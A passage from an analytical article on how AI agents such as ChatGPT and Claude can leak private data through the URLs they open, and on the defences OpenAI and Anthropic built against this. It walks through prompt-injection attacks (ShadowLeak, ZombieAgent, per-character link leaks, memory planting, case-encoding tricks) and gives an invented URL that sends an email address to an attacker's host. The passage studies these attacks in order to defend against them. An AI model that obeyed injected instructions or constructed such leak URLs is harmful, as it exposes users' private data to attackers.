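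OpenAI fixed the flaw in early August, about seven weeks after the report, without telling Radware. It acknowledged the flaw and marked it as resolved on 3 September. Radware published its findings on 18 September, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Zero-Click Vulnerability in ChatGPT's Agent Enables Silent Gmail Data Theft*.

### Opening URLs only as provided

Radware first described OpenAI's fix for ShadowLeak in its next report, on an attack it named ZombieAgent. According to Radware, OpenAI had prohibited ChatGPT from modifying URLs, so ChatGPT could open a URL only "exactly as provided" and would not add anything to it even when told to. Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data* also presents this rule as OpenAI's response to ShadowLeak.

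Neither account gives the date the rule took effect. It must have applied by 26 September 2025, when Radware reported a way around it. The rule may well have been the August repair, since Rehberger also noticed new restrictions on URLs at about that time.

When such a rule is enforced by an exact comparison of URLs, as described earlier, it stops ShadowLeak as soon as Deep Research adds the name and address to the attacker's URL. This works even if they are encoded first, because the comparison doesn't depend on recognising private data.

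Splitting the data into pieces doesn't help the attacker either, because adding even one character to a URL produces one that nobody provided. Splitting did get past simple filters in the *Silent Egress* tests.

The rule is therefore much better suited to preventing content leaks than the defences that Radware got past in June. How reliable it was depends on whether ordinary software compared the URLs or OpenAI had trained the model not to alter them. Radware writes that ChatGPT "refuses" to add parameters, which could describe either.

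The rule also did not limit who could provide a URL. URLs in emails counted, so anyone who knew a user's email address could add URLs to the set that ChatGPT would open. The same email could contain instructions for using them.

### ZombieAgent

Zvika Babo, one of the researchers behind ShadowLeak, took advantage of this with ZombieAgent, a selection leak. The attacker's email supplies the 37 fixed links from the earlier capacity calculation, each standing for one character. When the user asks for help with their inbox, ChatGPT reads the email and opens the links that spell out the private data. It copies every URL exactly, so the exact-URL rule allows every request.

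Rehberger and Tenable had used the technique before, but they needed fixed addresses that url_safe would accept. Under the exact-URL rule, all of the attacker's links worked as soon as the email arrived, however many there were. So for links prepared in advance, OpenAI's rule for opening pages was more permissive than its older check on displaying images.

The exact-URL rule still protected long documents reasonably well against ZombieAgent, though not names or login codes. One ShadowLeak request could carry a name and address together, whereas ZombieAgent needs a separate request for each character. A nine-letter name takes nine requests, which is practical, but a 2,000-character email would take 2,000. Radware therefore overstates the result when it calls ZombieAgent a full bypass and says that it makes OpenAI's defence "ineffective".

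Radware also leaked data through a file the user shared with ChatGPT, and through images in the user's browser. It found the images less reliable and easier to block, and focused on requests from OpenAI's servers.

### Links from memory

OpenAI was already restricting some links by their origin. According to Radware, ChatGPT would not open an attacker's URL that came from Memory, the feature that stores information about the user across conversations. OpenAI had also prevented ChatGPT from using Memory in a chat once it had used Connectors there.

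The separation worked in only one direction, so ChatGPT could still consult Memory first and use Connectors afterwards. Radware used a shared file to plant an instruction in Memory that made ChatGPT read the attacker's email at the start of every later exchange. The links came from the email rather than from Memory, so the restriction on opening URLs from Memory did not apply.

This turned a single leak into a continuing one. It also shows why a company can't judge each source of links in isolation. Text in a source whose links are barred can still direct the assistant to a source whose links it accepts, so barring links from Memory was of limited use while the assistant still accepted links from email.

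### The restriction on email links

Radware submitted ZombieAgent on 26 September 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that handles security reports for OpenAI. Three days later, Radware sent an improved version, which it said had a 100% success rate. Bugcrowd reproduced the attack on 30 September and passed the report to OpenAI. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December, 81 days after the first report, and Radware published its findings on 8 January 2026.

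The delay mattered because Connectors was reaching more people. It moved from a test version to general availability in December 2025, according to TechRadar's *This 'ZombieAgent' zero click vulnerability allows for silent account takeover*.

Radware's timeline gives the date of the fix but not how it works. The news article *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack* supplies the rule. ChatGPT may open a link that came from an email only if at least one of two conditions holds:

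- the link appears in a well-known public index;
- the user supplied the link directly in a chat message.

The Italian technology site Punto Informatico reports only the exception for links the user supplied. The version with both exceptions is probably complete, because it better matches the test for public URLs that OpenAI described in January 2026.

The table compares the two versions of the rule, on the assumption that OpenAI kept the ban on altering URLs when it restricted email links. This seems likely, but it isn't explicit in any of these accounts.

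| What ChatGPT tries to open | Exact-URL rule | After 16 December 2025 |
|---|---|---|
| A link from an email, with private data added | Blocked | Blocked |
| An attacker's unindexed link, exactly as in the email | Allowed | Blocked |
| A private document link from a colleague's email | Allowed | Blocked |
| A link from an email to an indexed news article | Allowed | Allowed |
| A link from an email to an attacker's indexed page | Allowed | Allowed |
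| Any of these unaltered links, if the user also pastes it into the chat | Allowed | Allowed |

OpenAI changed the rule on where a link may come from because the form of the attacker's links didn't distinguish them from ordinary ones. Ordinary newsletters are full of long, unfamiliar URLs that differ by only a few characters, and software can't determine from such a URL whether opening it will load an article or reveal a letter of someone's name. The revised rule doesn't require ChatGPT to make that distinction. ChatGPT won't open an unindexed URL that it found only in an email, but it will open the same URL if the user types it into the chat.

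Email was a natural source to restrict because an attacker can send a link to a chosen person's inbox, which also holds the private messages the attacker wants to read.

The restriction made ZombieAgent harder to carry out but did not rule out every version of it, because an attacker can still email links to pages already in the index.

It is less clear whether OpenAI also restricted links from other connected accounts. Radware warns that attackers could hide the same instructions in shared documents, support tickets or code repositories, and Punto Informatico notes that the fix blocks one specific attack. If OpenAI restricted only links from email, an attacker could have moved the list of links to a shared document. But the policy that OpenAI published six weeks later does not distinguish between email and other sources, so the restriction on email links may have been part of a broader check,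 which journalists described in terms of the attack that Radware had reported.

### Radware's account and OpenAI's

Nearly everything public about the two attacks comes from Radware, including the success rates, the wording of the exact-URL rule and the date of each fix. SecurityWeek's *‘ZombieAgent’ Attack Let Researchers Take Over ChatGPT* gives the same months for the report and the fix, but it attributes the findings to Radware and includes no comment from OpenAI. Infosecurity Magazine also relies on Radware's report, so the press coverage adds little independent evidence. Bugcrowd's reproduction of ZombieAgent is better evidence, but the only source for it is Radware's timeline.

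OpenAI wrote in its post of 28 January 2026 that if a URL is not in its index, ChatGPT either looks for another website or warns the user before the URL opens. This supports the exception for indexed links. However, OpenAI does not mention Radware, either attack, or a special rule for email in the post, so it doesn't establish what OpenAI changed on 16 December.

OpenAI has also acknowledged the weakness behind ZombieAgent. According to Rehberger on Embrace The Red, the company points out in its technical paper that an attacker can use a separate URL for each letter. This makes Radware's central technical claim credible even without a statement from OpenAI about the incident.

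Radware sells security products, and it was recruiting customers to test one for AI agents on the same web pages where it describes the attacks, so its recommendations deserve more caution than its technical findings. In an advisory published with the ZombieAgent report, Radware criticizes AI companies' safeguards as "largely rule-based and reactive" and recommends monitoring an agent's behaviour for actions that depart from what the user wanted.

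Critics can fairly call OpenAI reactive. The company repaired each flaw after Radware reported it, even though Rehberger had publicly described leaks through fixed URLs in 2023. But ZombieAgent is weak evidence against having URL rules at all. The exact-URL rule failed because it allowed links from strangers' emails, and OpenAI could correct that with a better rule.

Monitoring might have caught ZombieAgent, since summarizing an inbox doesn't require opening dozens of nearly identical pages. It would be less likely to catch the leaks that Liang and colleagues demonstrated, because those agents opened only links relevant to the user's question, as users expect a research assistant to do.

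## OpenAI's rule that a URL must already be public

When OpenAI restricted email links in December 2025, it made an exception for links in a public index. On 28 January 2026, the company presented such an index as its general test for automatic loading. Adrian Spânu and Thomas Shadwell, writing for OpenAI, explain that ChatGPT may load a URL automatically only if a crawler has already recorded that exact URL on the public web. The rule applies equally to URLs on famous sites and URLs from trusted colleagues.

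### The index and the check

A crawler is a program that follows links across the web, and a *public index* is the record of the URLs it finds. OpenAI's crawler has no access to users' conversations, accounts or personal data, so it learns about pages the way a search engine does. On Embrace The Red, Rehberger summarises the accompanying technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. He writes that ChatGPT may open any URL that the crawler has encountered. In 2023 he guessed that OpenAI was consulting Bing's index, but OpenAI now has its own.

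OpenAI applies the check when the agent is about to retrieve something by itself, such as an article or an image:

1. OpenAI's software looks for the URL in the index.
2. If the URL matches one that the crawler recorded, ChatGPT loads it without asking.
3. If nothing matches, OpenAI treats the URL as unverified. It either tells the agent to try a different website or shows the user a warning before the URL opens.

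OpenAI doesn't explain in the post how it chooses between another website and a warning.

A user can also allow ChatGPT to fetch a URL by typing it in a message. Rehberger's impression is that ChatGPT has for a while treated such a URL as safe for the rest of the chat session.

It is unclear when the rule took effect. Rehberger says the paper describes measures OpenAI added around August 2025, but ZombieAgent still worked in late September with links from an email. If both accounts are right, OpenAI checked some requests against the index months before it checked others.

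### Three URLs under the rule

Suppose a user has connected their email account and asks ChatGPT for background on a local bridge repair. In the course of the work, the agent tries to open three invented URLs:

- `news.example/2026/01/harbour-bridge-reopens`, a newspaper article;
- `files.example/s/q7Rk2vX9`, a private document link that a colleague created ten minutes ago and sent by email;
- `attacker.example/collect?data=maria@mail.example`, which the model constructed from the user's email address because a web page contained hidden instructions to do so.

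The newspaper links to the article from its front page, so the crawler has probably found it, and ChatGPT opens it. If the article is only a few minutes old, the crawler may not have found it yet, and ChatGPT may have to look for another report.

The crawler can't have recorded the colleague's link, because no public page contains it. Trying another website won't help, since the document exists in only one place. If ChatGPT shows the warning, the user can recognise the file service, remember asking for the document, and open it.

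The constructed URL isn't in the index, so OpenAI's software treats it the same way as the colleague's link. If the agent moves on to another website, the attack fails and the user may never know about it. If the warning appears, the user can see their own email address at the end of an unfamiliar URL.

### Why earlier publication is evidence

The constructed URL can be in the index only if somebody published it with Maria's email address already in it, which requires knowing the address before the conversation began. An attacker who doesn't know the address can't publish the URL before or during the conversation.

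OpenAI claims only that a public URL is "much less likely" to contain the user's private data. It is right to be cautious, because people sometimes publish private URLs by accident, for example by pasting a link that contains a login token into a public forum. A crawler can record that link, and ChatGPT could then open it without a warning. The site's owner would learn little from the URL itself, because the owner issued it, but the page might contain private material. On badly designed sites, opening a link can also cancel a booking or confirm a subscription.

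An attacker can also publish a page for every possible answer beforehand. If the attacker publishes a hundred pages, one for each age from 1 to 100, the model can write the user's age into a URL and the software will find a match. The URL passes even though the model constructed it, because the check compares only the finished URL. This is a selection leak, so the attacker needs a separate page for each answer that a single request can reveal, such as 500 pages to learn which of 500 employees is asking.

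A URL can reveal something about the user even when there is no attacker. OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links* describes a user who asks where to buy a car and receives a link to `example.com/car_search/London`, because ChatGPT knows they live in London. Opening the link reveals their city to the car site. A real car site would probably have a public page for London, so the crawler could well have recorded its URL. ChatGPT could then open it without asking, even though the request would connect this user to London.

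The evidence also depends on keeping the URLs that users request out of the index. OpenAI uses separate programs for crawling and for fetching pages on demand. According to Search Engine Journal, OAI-SearchBot determines whether a site appears in ChatGPT's search results, and the on-demand fetcher, ChatGPT-User, does not. If OpenAI added the URLs that ChatGPT-User fetches to the index, one person's approval of a private link would allow that link for everyone. OpenAI avoids this by keeping the crawler away from conversations.

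### What counts as the same URL

Two URLs can differ as text and still lead to the same page. text/plain's *Guidelines for URL Storage and Comparison* (2026), which discusses security software such as Microsoft's SmartScreen, cautions against treating URLs as plain strings. For instance, capitalization doesn't matter in a domain name but can matter in the path. Links in newsletters often end in a tracking code that has no effect on the page. Software that requires identical text will reject some harmless variants and cause needless warnings.

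A loose comparison is more dangerous. If the software ignored the query string, the model could put Maria's email address there and the URL would still match. Even if it ignored only capitalization in the path, the model could leak data by choosing upper or lower case for each letter. A recorded URL with 40 letters in its path could then carry 40 bits, enough for two six-digit login codes, and the attacker's log would preserve the capitals. A developer can prevent this by requesting the recorded version of the URL instead of the model's version. OpenAI refers to "this exact URL" in its post but doesn't explain how it handles such variants.

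### OpenAI's case against trusted-site lists

OpenAI considered the simpler rule of letting an agent open links only to well-known websites. It says this helps, but points out that many legitimate sites have redirects. A link can start on a trusted domain and immediately forward the visitor to the attacker's site, and checking only the first domain won't detect this. ChatGPT's older check failed this way when Tenable used forwarding addresses on bing.com.

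This argument applies more to careless lists than to lists in general, since software could check every domain in a chain of redirects. But a missed redirect does less harm under OpenAI's rule. Some sites have a forwarding page that takes its destination from the query string, and an attacker could get the model to write a destination there that includes Maria's email address. A site list that checks only the first domain would allow the request, but OpenAI's rule would block it because the crawler has never recorded that complete URL.

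A recorded URL may also redirect, and OpenAI doesn't say in the post whether it also checks the destination. The redirecting server usually has only the information in the recorded URL, so it has no email address to pass on unless the user is logged in to that site.

OpenAI also objects that a strict list would produce frequent false alarms, because people visit far more than a handful of popular sites. It expects people who see too many warnings to start clicking through them without thinking, including the ones that matter. An index of the public web can cover many more pages than a list that staff have to inspect, so it should interrupt people less. However, OpenAI gives no figures for either method, and the index also produces false alarms, on new and private pages.

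Even OpenAI's own domain can host a harmful page, a problem that an index of public URLs doesn't solve either. eWeek's *ChatGPT Share Links Abused Through Real OpenAI URLs* reports that attackers used a shared-content page on chatgpt.com to display a fake outage notice urging visitors to download an app.

OpenAI still uses site lists for some products. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026) shows a settings screen where developers can list the domains that Codex may contact. Such a list is easier to manage for a coding agent, which may need only a few sites for documentation and software packages.

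Apps that other companies build for ChatGPT can declare domains too. In *Verifying URLs used in apps*, a thread on OpenAI's developer forum, a developer complains that users get a warning every time they click a link in the developer's app, but not in Booking.com's or Uber's. The answer refers to the redirect_domains setting, where developers list the sites their app links to. OpenAI says the function that opens these links is for "vetted" links. If the vetting covers only the domain, a URL could carry private data to any declared site, so OpenAI has to trust whoever runs that site.

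### What the warning can and can't do

The warning, titled "Check this link is safe", states that ChatGPT hasn't verified the link and that opening it may share data from the conversation with another site. It also displays the URL, with options to copy or open it. OpenAI advises users who notice anything odd not to open the link and to ask ChatGPT for another source or a summary.

This lets the user stop a request that would otherwise happen in the background, but only if they recognise the private data in the URL. An email address is easy to spot, but the ShadowLeak attack encoded the data first, and few people would recognise their own name and address in a string of random-looking characters. OpenAI's check also doesn't apply if the user copies the link into another browser.

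If a website's owner asks OpenAI not to catalogue its pages, ChatGPT shows the warning and asks the user to confirm every link to that site, according to the help page. OpenAI's argument about false alarms applies here, because a person who regularly uses such a site will see the warning many times for harmless links and may have stopped reading it by the time an attacker's link appears.

Users can also mistake the warning for a judgement on the site. In March 2026, ChatGPT flagged links to WinRed, a fundraising platform for the US Republican Party, as potentially unsafe, but did not flag similar links to its Democratic counterpart, ActBlue. An OECD database lists the incident as *ChatGPT Flags Republican Fundraising Links as Unsafe, Raising Bias Concerns* (2026). According to the entry's AI-generated summary, OpenAI blamed a technical glitch, and the incident raised concerns about political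 bias. A gap in the index could have caused the difference without any political bias, but the entry doesn't establish that it did.

### Safe Url in March 2026

In March 2026, OpenAI described Safe Url as a way to detect when information the assistant learned in a conversation would go to a third party. ChatGPT then either shows the user the information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and tells the agent to continue another way. OpenAI says such cases are rare.

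This doesn't quite match the test from January, in which OpenAI uses the index as a practical substitute for recognising private information in a URL. A public page that the crawler missed fails the test even though it contains nothing private. The London car search probably passes, although it reveals something ChatGPT learned from the user.

OpenAI doesn't rely on screening what the assistant reads. Some companies sell "AI firewalls", which try to separate malicious instructions from ordinary text. OpenAI says these systems don't usually catch fully developed attacks, because detecting one is the same problem as detecting a lie, often without the necessary context.

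Bookmarks in the Atlas browser need this check as much as navigation does, because an attacker could get the agent to save a URL containing private data, which would leak when the user clicked the bookmark days later. Safe Url also covers searches in Deep Research, but it is less clear how an index could help there, since the model has usually just written the query. OpenAI doesn't explain in the March post how Safe Url decides whether a query is safe.

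ChatGPT Apps and Canvas, a workspace for writing and code, use a related method. They run programs in a sandbox, which is closed off from the rest of the system. The sandbox can detect unexpected communication and prompt the user for consent.

There is little independent evidence of how well these protections work together. In *The Framing Gap*, ChatGPT leaked nothing in 48 valid trials, while the model the researchers reached through the API leaked in up to 100% of trials. If the trials were independent, ChatGPT's true leak rate could still be as high as about 6%, at 95% confidence. The researchers couldn't see inside ChatGPT and don't attribute the result to any particular defence.

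On 20 February 2026, OpenAI fixed a flaw outside URL loading that could secretly leak a conversation's messages and uploaded files. The Hacker News (2026) says the security company Check Point discovered the flaw, and reports no evidence that anyone had used it maliciously.

### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI introduced a stricter, optional setting called Lockdown Mode on 13 February 2026. It was first available to organisations, including companies, schools and healthcare providers. Help Net Security's *OpenAI is locking down parts of ChatGPT to reduce data theft risks* (2026) reports that OpenAI began offering it on personal accounts, including free ones, in June. In this mode, ChatGPT can browse only cached pages, which are copies that OpenAI already holds, so no live request leaves OpenAI's network when ChatGPT reads one.

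This prevents the selection leaks that the index rule allows. An attacker can still influence which page ChatGPT reads, but their server receives no request, so the attacker learns nothing from the choice. Liang and colleagues had their system download every linked page in advance to get a similar result.

| What ChatGPT tries to do | Ordinary settings | Lockdown Mode |
|---|---|---|
| Read the newspaper article | Loads it if the crawler recorded the URL | Reads OpenAI's copy, if there is one |
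| Open the colleague's new private link | Tries another site or warns the user | Makes no live request |
| Open the constructed URL | Tries another site or warns the user | Makes no live request |
| Choose among an attacker's recorded pages | Loads the page, and the attacker sees which | Reads OpenAI's copy, and the attacker sees nothing |

The tradeoff is that search results may be out of date or missing, and ChatGPT may not show images from the web. OpenAI also disables Deep Research and Agent Mode, in which ChatGPT carries out tasks on websites. ChatGPT can't download files for data analysis, but it can still work with files the user uploads, and memory works as before.

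Willison (2026) thinks the design of Lockdown Mode looks very good, because its restrictions are deterministic and don't depend on an AI model that an attacker could manipulate. He also infers from the mode's existence that ChatGPT's default settings don't give robust protection against a determined attacker. That seems fair, given what the index rule allows. OpenAI says most users don't need the mode. Its head of security, Dane Stuckey, recommends it to people who face a higher risk because of who they are, their work or the data they handle.

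Connected apps are harder to lock down than web browsing. In June, personal accounts could still use connectors whose data OpenAI had already copied, because searching a stored copy sends no live request to the outside service. OpenAI's current help page, *Lockdown Mode*, is less specific. It says that on personal accounts the mode blocks apps from accessing outside services live or making changes there when doing so would conflict with the mode's protections.

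In workspaces that an organisation manages, Lockdown Mode doesn't disable every app automatically, and administrators must decide which ones to allow. OpenAI advises them not to let an app write anything a malicious outsider might be able to see, which would rule out posts on a public page.

Lockdown Mode doesn't restrict Codex's network access, and people with personal accounts can switch it off for a single chat. OpenAI also warns that it can't guarantee that no data will leak, since risks may remain in enabled apps, unexpected combinations of features, or undiscovered techniques. TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reports that Check Point has since found a way around the mode and that OpenAI fixed the flaw on its servers. *ChatGPT Lockdown Mode Bypass Exfiltrates Chats Without User Interaction* (2026), from the IT services company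 Capstone Technologies Group, dates the fix to 18 September 2026.

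## Anthropic's web fetch tool for developers

Developers use Anthropic's fetch tool, web_fetch, through the API, the interface that lets their own programs send requests to Claude. The API refuses to fetch a URL that hasn't already appeared in the conversation, whereas OpenAI checks a URL against a record of the public web. Anthropic's *Release Notes* (2025) date the tool's beta release to 10 September 2025. Developers decide what private data Claude sees and which of the tool's optional limits to use, so the protection varies between products.

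Anthropic has since released three more versions. According to Anthropic's *Web fetch 工具*, the Chinese edition of the documentation from November 2026, all four remain available:

| Version | What it added |
|---|---|
| web_fetch_20250910 | Basic fetching |
| web_fetch_20260209 | Dynamic filtering, in which Claude writes code to trim a page before reading it |
| web_fetch_20260309 | An option to bypass the cache |
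| web_fetch_20260318 | An option to leave some fetched pages out of the API's response |

### From the model's request to the page's text

Anthropic runs web_fetch on its own computers and calls it a *server tool* for that reason. A developer's program only has to list the tool in its request. A fetch then goes as follows:

1. Claude decides that it needs a page and writes a tool call containing the URL. It does this when the user points to a particular page or document, and answers general questions directly.
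2. The API checks the URL against the provenance rule and any limits the developer has set.
3. If the URL passes, the API retrieves the page or takes a stored copy from its cache. If it fails, the API returns an error code and doesn't request the page.
4. The page's text or the error code becomes part of the conversation, and Claude continues with its answer.

Anthropic doesn't specify the order of the checks in the second step, but the order should only affect which error code Claude receives when a URL breaks several rules.

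| Error code | Cause |
|---|---|
| invalid_tool_input | The URL is malformed or isn't a web address |
| url_not_in_prior_context | The URL hasn't appeared in an accepted link source |
| url_not_allowed | A domain list or one of Anthropic's own restrictions blocks the URL |
| url_too_long | The URL has more than 250 characters |
| max_uses_exceeded | Claude has used up its fetches |
| url_not_accessible | The site returned an error |
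| unsupported_content_type | The file isn't text, HTML or PDF |
| content_too_large | A PDF would take the request over its size or page limit |
| too_many_requests | The program has exceeded its rate limit |
| unavailable | Anthropic's system had an internal error |

Anthropic itself blocks addresses on private networks and pages that a site's robots.txt file closes to automated visitors. The API normally returns the errors url_not_accessible, unsupported_content_type and content_too_large after it has contacted the site, so an attacker's server may have logged the URL even though Claude never received a page.

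In June 2026, Anthropic listed no separate error code for URLs that failed the provenance rule. By August it had added `url_not_in_prior_context`, which lets developers distinguish these URLs from those on blocked domains. Repeated errors of this kind may mean that hidden instructions are leading Claude to construct URLs, although a model can also guess a URL without such instructions.

### The three accepted link sources

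Claude can fetch a URL only if it has already appeared in one of these places:

- a user message;
- a *client-side tool result*, which is output that the developer's own program passes back to Claude;
- the result of an earlier web search or web fetch.

The API rejects URLs that appear only in Claude's own output or in results from Anthropic's other server tools, such as the code execution tool, which runs programs in an isolated container, and the MCP connector, which links Claude to outside services. It also rejects URLs that appear only in the system prompt, the developer's standing instructions to the model, unless the developer repeats them in a user message.

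As Willison pointed out when the tool was released, developers often insert outside text into user messages, so a web address in one may not have come from the user.

Client-side tool results have a similar problem. If a developer writes a tool that reads the user's inbox, every link in the emails it returns becomes an admitted URL, including links from strangers. ChatGPT allowed the same thing when Radware demonstrated ZombieAgent. If the developer connects the same inbox through the MCP connector, none of those links are admitted, because the rule depends on whose computers ran the tool, not who wrote the text.

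A developer's own tool can also undermine the ban on constructed URLs. Anthropic acknowledges that results from client-side tools count by default as accepted sources of URLs, even when they repeat text that Claude wrote. A tool that runs code for Claude returns whatever the code prints, including any URL that Claude put there. An error message that quotes Claude's command has the same effect. This again allows the content leak that the ban is meant to prevent.

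As a partial safeguard, Anthropic's API refuses a URL that seems to contain a credential, such as a password or an API key, unless the credential appears in the system prompt or in the text of a user message. It would therefore refuse a URL containing a key that Claude found in a file through one of the developer's tools. But the check works only if the software recognises the key, and Radware got past a similar defence in Deep Research by encoding the data. The check also doesn't cover names or email addresses, which aren't credentials.

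### Links on fetched pages since July 2026

In July 2026, Anthropic stopped the Claude app from following links on fetched pages, but it did not change the default for developers. Anthropic still accepted these links in its documentation of 11 August and still does in the November edition. Anthropic's *網頁擷取工具*, a second Chinese translation from November, lists the same accepted sources.

Between August and November, Anthropic did add a setting to the documentation, url_sources, with which developers can switch sources off:

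| Key | URLs it controls | What the developer can accept |
|---|---|---|
| user_input | Those in user messages | All or none |
| client_tool_results | Those in results from the developer's tools | All, none, only named tools, or all except named tools |
| server_tool_results | Those in earlier search and fetch results | The same choices, naming web_search or web_fetch |

Every key defaults to "all". A developer can exclude links on fetched pages by setting server_tool_results to accept only web_search. Claude can then open a search result but not a link on that page, unless the link has also appeared in another accepted source. A developer whose program runs Claude's code can also exclude the results of the tool that runs it. Other tools may repeat Claude's text too, so only setting client_tool_results to "none" fully protects against URLs that Claude wrote and a tool repeated.

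Under "except", any tool a developer adds later automatically becomes an accepted link source. "Only" is safer because it excludes new tools until the developer adds them to the setting, so forgetting to update it blocks a fetch instead of allowing a leak.

Anthropic gives no reason in the documentation for keeping the old default. Changing it would have broken programs that follow links, and developers can restrict fetching to named sites. But a developer who never looks at url_sources gets no benefit from it. If that developer also hasn't set a domain list, an attacker whose page Claude opens can still supply new links at every step, as in Paul's attack on the app.

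Anthropic made the same choice for Claude Managed Agents, a product in which it runs much of the agent's machinery for the developer. Anthropic's *Claude Platform release notes* (2026) announce that from 7 October, six months after the beta launch, the product's fetch tool opens only URLs that have already appeared in the session. Anthropic cites the risk of exfiltration. This version of the rule is stricter about tools and files. It rejects URLs that appear only in attached documents or in the output of command-line, file-reading and MCP tools, but still accepts links on pages the agent fetched earlier.

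Managed Agents also turns web_fetch on by default and doesn't offer max_uses, which caps the number of fetches. Developers can instead restrict which sites the tool may fetch, or limit fetches indirectly by setting a budget that pauses the session once its spending reaches a fixed amount.

### Domain lists and look-alike names

A developer can use allowed_domains to list the only domains Claude may fetch from, or blocked_domains to list those it may not, but a request can't use both. An allowed list applies even to admitted URLs. A blocked list gives much less protection against exfiltration, because an attacker can register a new domain.

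Anthropic's *Server tools* explains that an entry for a domain also covers its subdomains. For the invented company Widget, an entry for `widget.example` covers `docs.widget.example` and every other subdomain, but an entry for `docs.widget.example` does not cover the main site or its other subdomains. Web fetch compares entries only with a URL's domain, so an entry with a path, such as `widget.example/manual`, never matches.

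Developers will probably notice that mistake in an allowed list, because it blocks pages they wanted, but it is easier to miss in a blocked list, where it blocks nothing. Some developers may well have such entries, since Anthropic told them during the beta that paths were supported.

Since 20 October 2026, an organisation's administrators can set domain lists for web fetch or turn the tool off. According to Anthropic's release notes, a URL in Managed Agents must pass both the organisation's list and the agent's own, and so must the destination of any redirect. Checking the destination addresses the weakness that Tenable exploited in url_safe. Anthropic doesn't mention redirects in its documentation of web fetch for the ordinary API.

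Anthropic also warned about lookalike domains in its beta documentation. Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, treats the Latin "a" and the Cyrillic "а" as different characters, although they look the same in most fonts. A version of amazon.com with the Cyrillic letter is therefore a separate domain that someone else could own.

Software can tell the two names apart, but a developer reading the list may not notice the difference. Claude can fetch from the look-alike domain if the developer copies it into allowed_domains, or if blocked_domains contains only the genuine name. Programs may also convert such names differently, so the filter could check one domain while the request goes to another. Anthropic advises developers to use ASCII names (only unaccented Latin letters, digits and hyphens) where possible, and to test and audit their lists.

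### Limits on number, length and content

The max_uses parameter caps the number of fetches in one turn, which is roughly everything Claude does in response to one user message. Without it, there is no cap. Failed fetches count toward the cap, and they should, because they can leak data too. But the count resets each turn. Five fetches from 37 fixed URLs can reveal at most 26 bits, so 20 such turns can reveal up to about 520 bits.

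The 250-character maximum limits how much data a constructed URL could carry if the tool fetched one. It has little effect on selection leaks, because their URLs can be short, and it blocks some legitimate pages.

The max_content_tokens parameter limits how much of a page's text enters the conversation. Tokens are the short pieces of text that a model processes. Anthropic estimates that an ordinary web page has about 2,500 tokens and a large documentation page about 25,000. The limit is approximate and doesn't apply to PDFs. It mainly helps control cost, since Anthropic charges for the tokens but not for the fetch. It offers little protection against a leak, because the request has already gone out before the text is cut, and an attacker's instructions can fit into a few sentences near the top of the page.

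Setting use_cache to false makes the API request a fresh copy each time, which removes the cache's incidental protection against repeated requests. Anthropic recommends this only when the user asks for current content or the page changes quickly, because it slows the fetch.

Leaving the cache on can make answers out of date. Classmethod's *The story about how Claude's Web Fetch tool doesn't necessarily return the latest information* reports that Claude kept citing limits of 101 rows and 10,000 characters from Slack's documentation, although the page gave 201 rows and 20,000 characters. The writer thinks the cache was the most likely cause.

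### How dynamic filtering affects URLs

From web_fetch_20260209 onwards, Claude can write a program that fetches a page and keeps only the relevant part. Claude calls web_fetch this way by default in these versions. Like Claude, a program can assemble a URL, but the output of Anthropic's code container isn't an accepted link source, so the API should refuse a URL that has appeared only there.

Dynamic filtering weakens the max_uses cap. A turn can span several API requests, for instance when Claude pauses during a long task. Fetches that Claude made directly in an earlier request still count towards the cap, but those it made from a program don't.

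It can also make a leak harder to investigate. In the newest version, a developer can set response_inclusion to "excluded", which removes completed fetches of this kind, including their URLs, from the API's response. This helps if the program doesn't need the raw pages, but a developer who relies on saved responses would have no record of where Claude sent those requests.

Developers can avoid both problems by setting allowed_callers to "direct", which turns off dynamic filtering, but Claude then has to read more of each page, which costs more.

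### Anthropic's advice to disable the tool

Despite these limits, Anthropic warned in documentation from the beta period and again in August 2026 that web_fetch could be used to exfiltrate data when Claude handles untrusted input alongside sensitive data. It told developers to use the tool only in trusted environments or with data that isn't sensitive. If exfiltration is a concern, Anthropic suggests disabling the tool, capping requests with max_uses, or restricting the domains it can fetch from.

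Disabling the tool makes sense for a program that reads confidential files and doesn't need the web. But most web pages are untrusted input, so taken literally, the warning rules out sensitive data in almost any program that browses freely. A developer who needs both sensitive data and web access should at least set allowed_domains, the only one of these limits that can keep requests away from an attacker's server no matter how the URL entered the conversation.

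### A documentation assistant

Suppose Widget builds an assistant that answers customers' questions from its online manual at `docs.widget.example`. The assistant also has web search and a tool that returns customers' support tickets. The tickets contain private details, and anyone can submit one. Widget could configure web_fetch like this:

```json
{
  "type": "web_fetch_20260318",
  "name": "web_fetch",
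  "allowed_callers": ["direct"],
  "allowed_domains": ["docs.widget.example"],
  "max_uses": 3,
  "max_content_tokens": 25000,
  "url_sources": {
    "client_tool_results": { "type": "none" }
  }
}
```

Claude tries six URLs, each in a separate turn. All begin with `https://`, which the table omits:

| URL | Where it appeared | Result |
|---|---|---|
| `docs.widget.example/install` | A customer's message | Fetched |
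| `docs.widget.example/errors/504` | A link on the installation page | Fetched |
| `forum.widget.example/t/88` | A search result | Blocked by allowed_domains |
| `docs.widget.example/reset` | A support ticket only | Blocked by url_sources |
| `docs.widget.example/search?q=maria@mail.example` | Only in Claude's own output | Blocked by the provenance rule |
| A 310-character link to the manual | A customer's message | Blocked by the length limit |

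The forum page can appear in search results because Widget restricted only web_fetch, and web_search has its own domain list. Widget was right to list `docs.widget.example` because listing `widget.example` would have let Claude fetch posts from a forum where strangers can write. If the forum were at `docs.widget.example/forum`, Widget couldn't exclude it, because web fetch doesn't filter by path.

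If Claude tried all six in one turn, in the order of the table, it would get two pages and one error, and the API would refuse the other three with max_uses_exceeded.

The link on the installation page passes because Widget left server_tool_results at its default. The default is fairly safe here, since such a link can lead only to another page of the manual, and an attacker can't normally read Widget's logs. If Widget later removed allowed_domains so that the assistant could research other companies' products, the forum page would pass, and so would links on it to an attacker's site. Widget should then set server_tool_results to accept only web_search. Claude could still open pages that an attacker had got into the search results, but it could no longer follow new links from those pages.

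## The Claude app, and why links on fetched pages were withdrawn

Developers can decide whether Claude may open links it finds on fetched pages. In the Claude app, Anthropic decides for everyone, and by mid-July 2026 it had stopped Claude from opening such links. It did so after Paul showed that a hostile website could use them to extract what Claude remembered about its user.

### Memory next to a fetch tool

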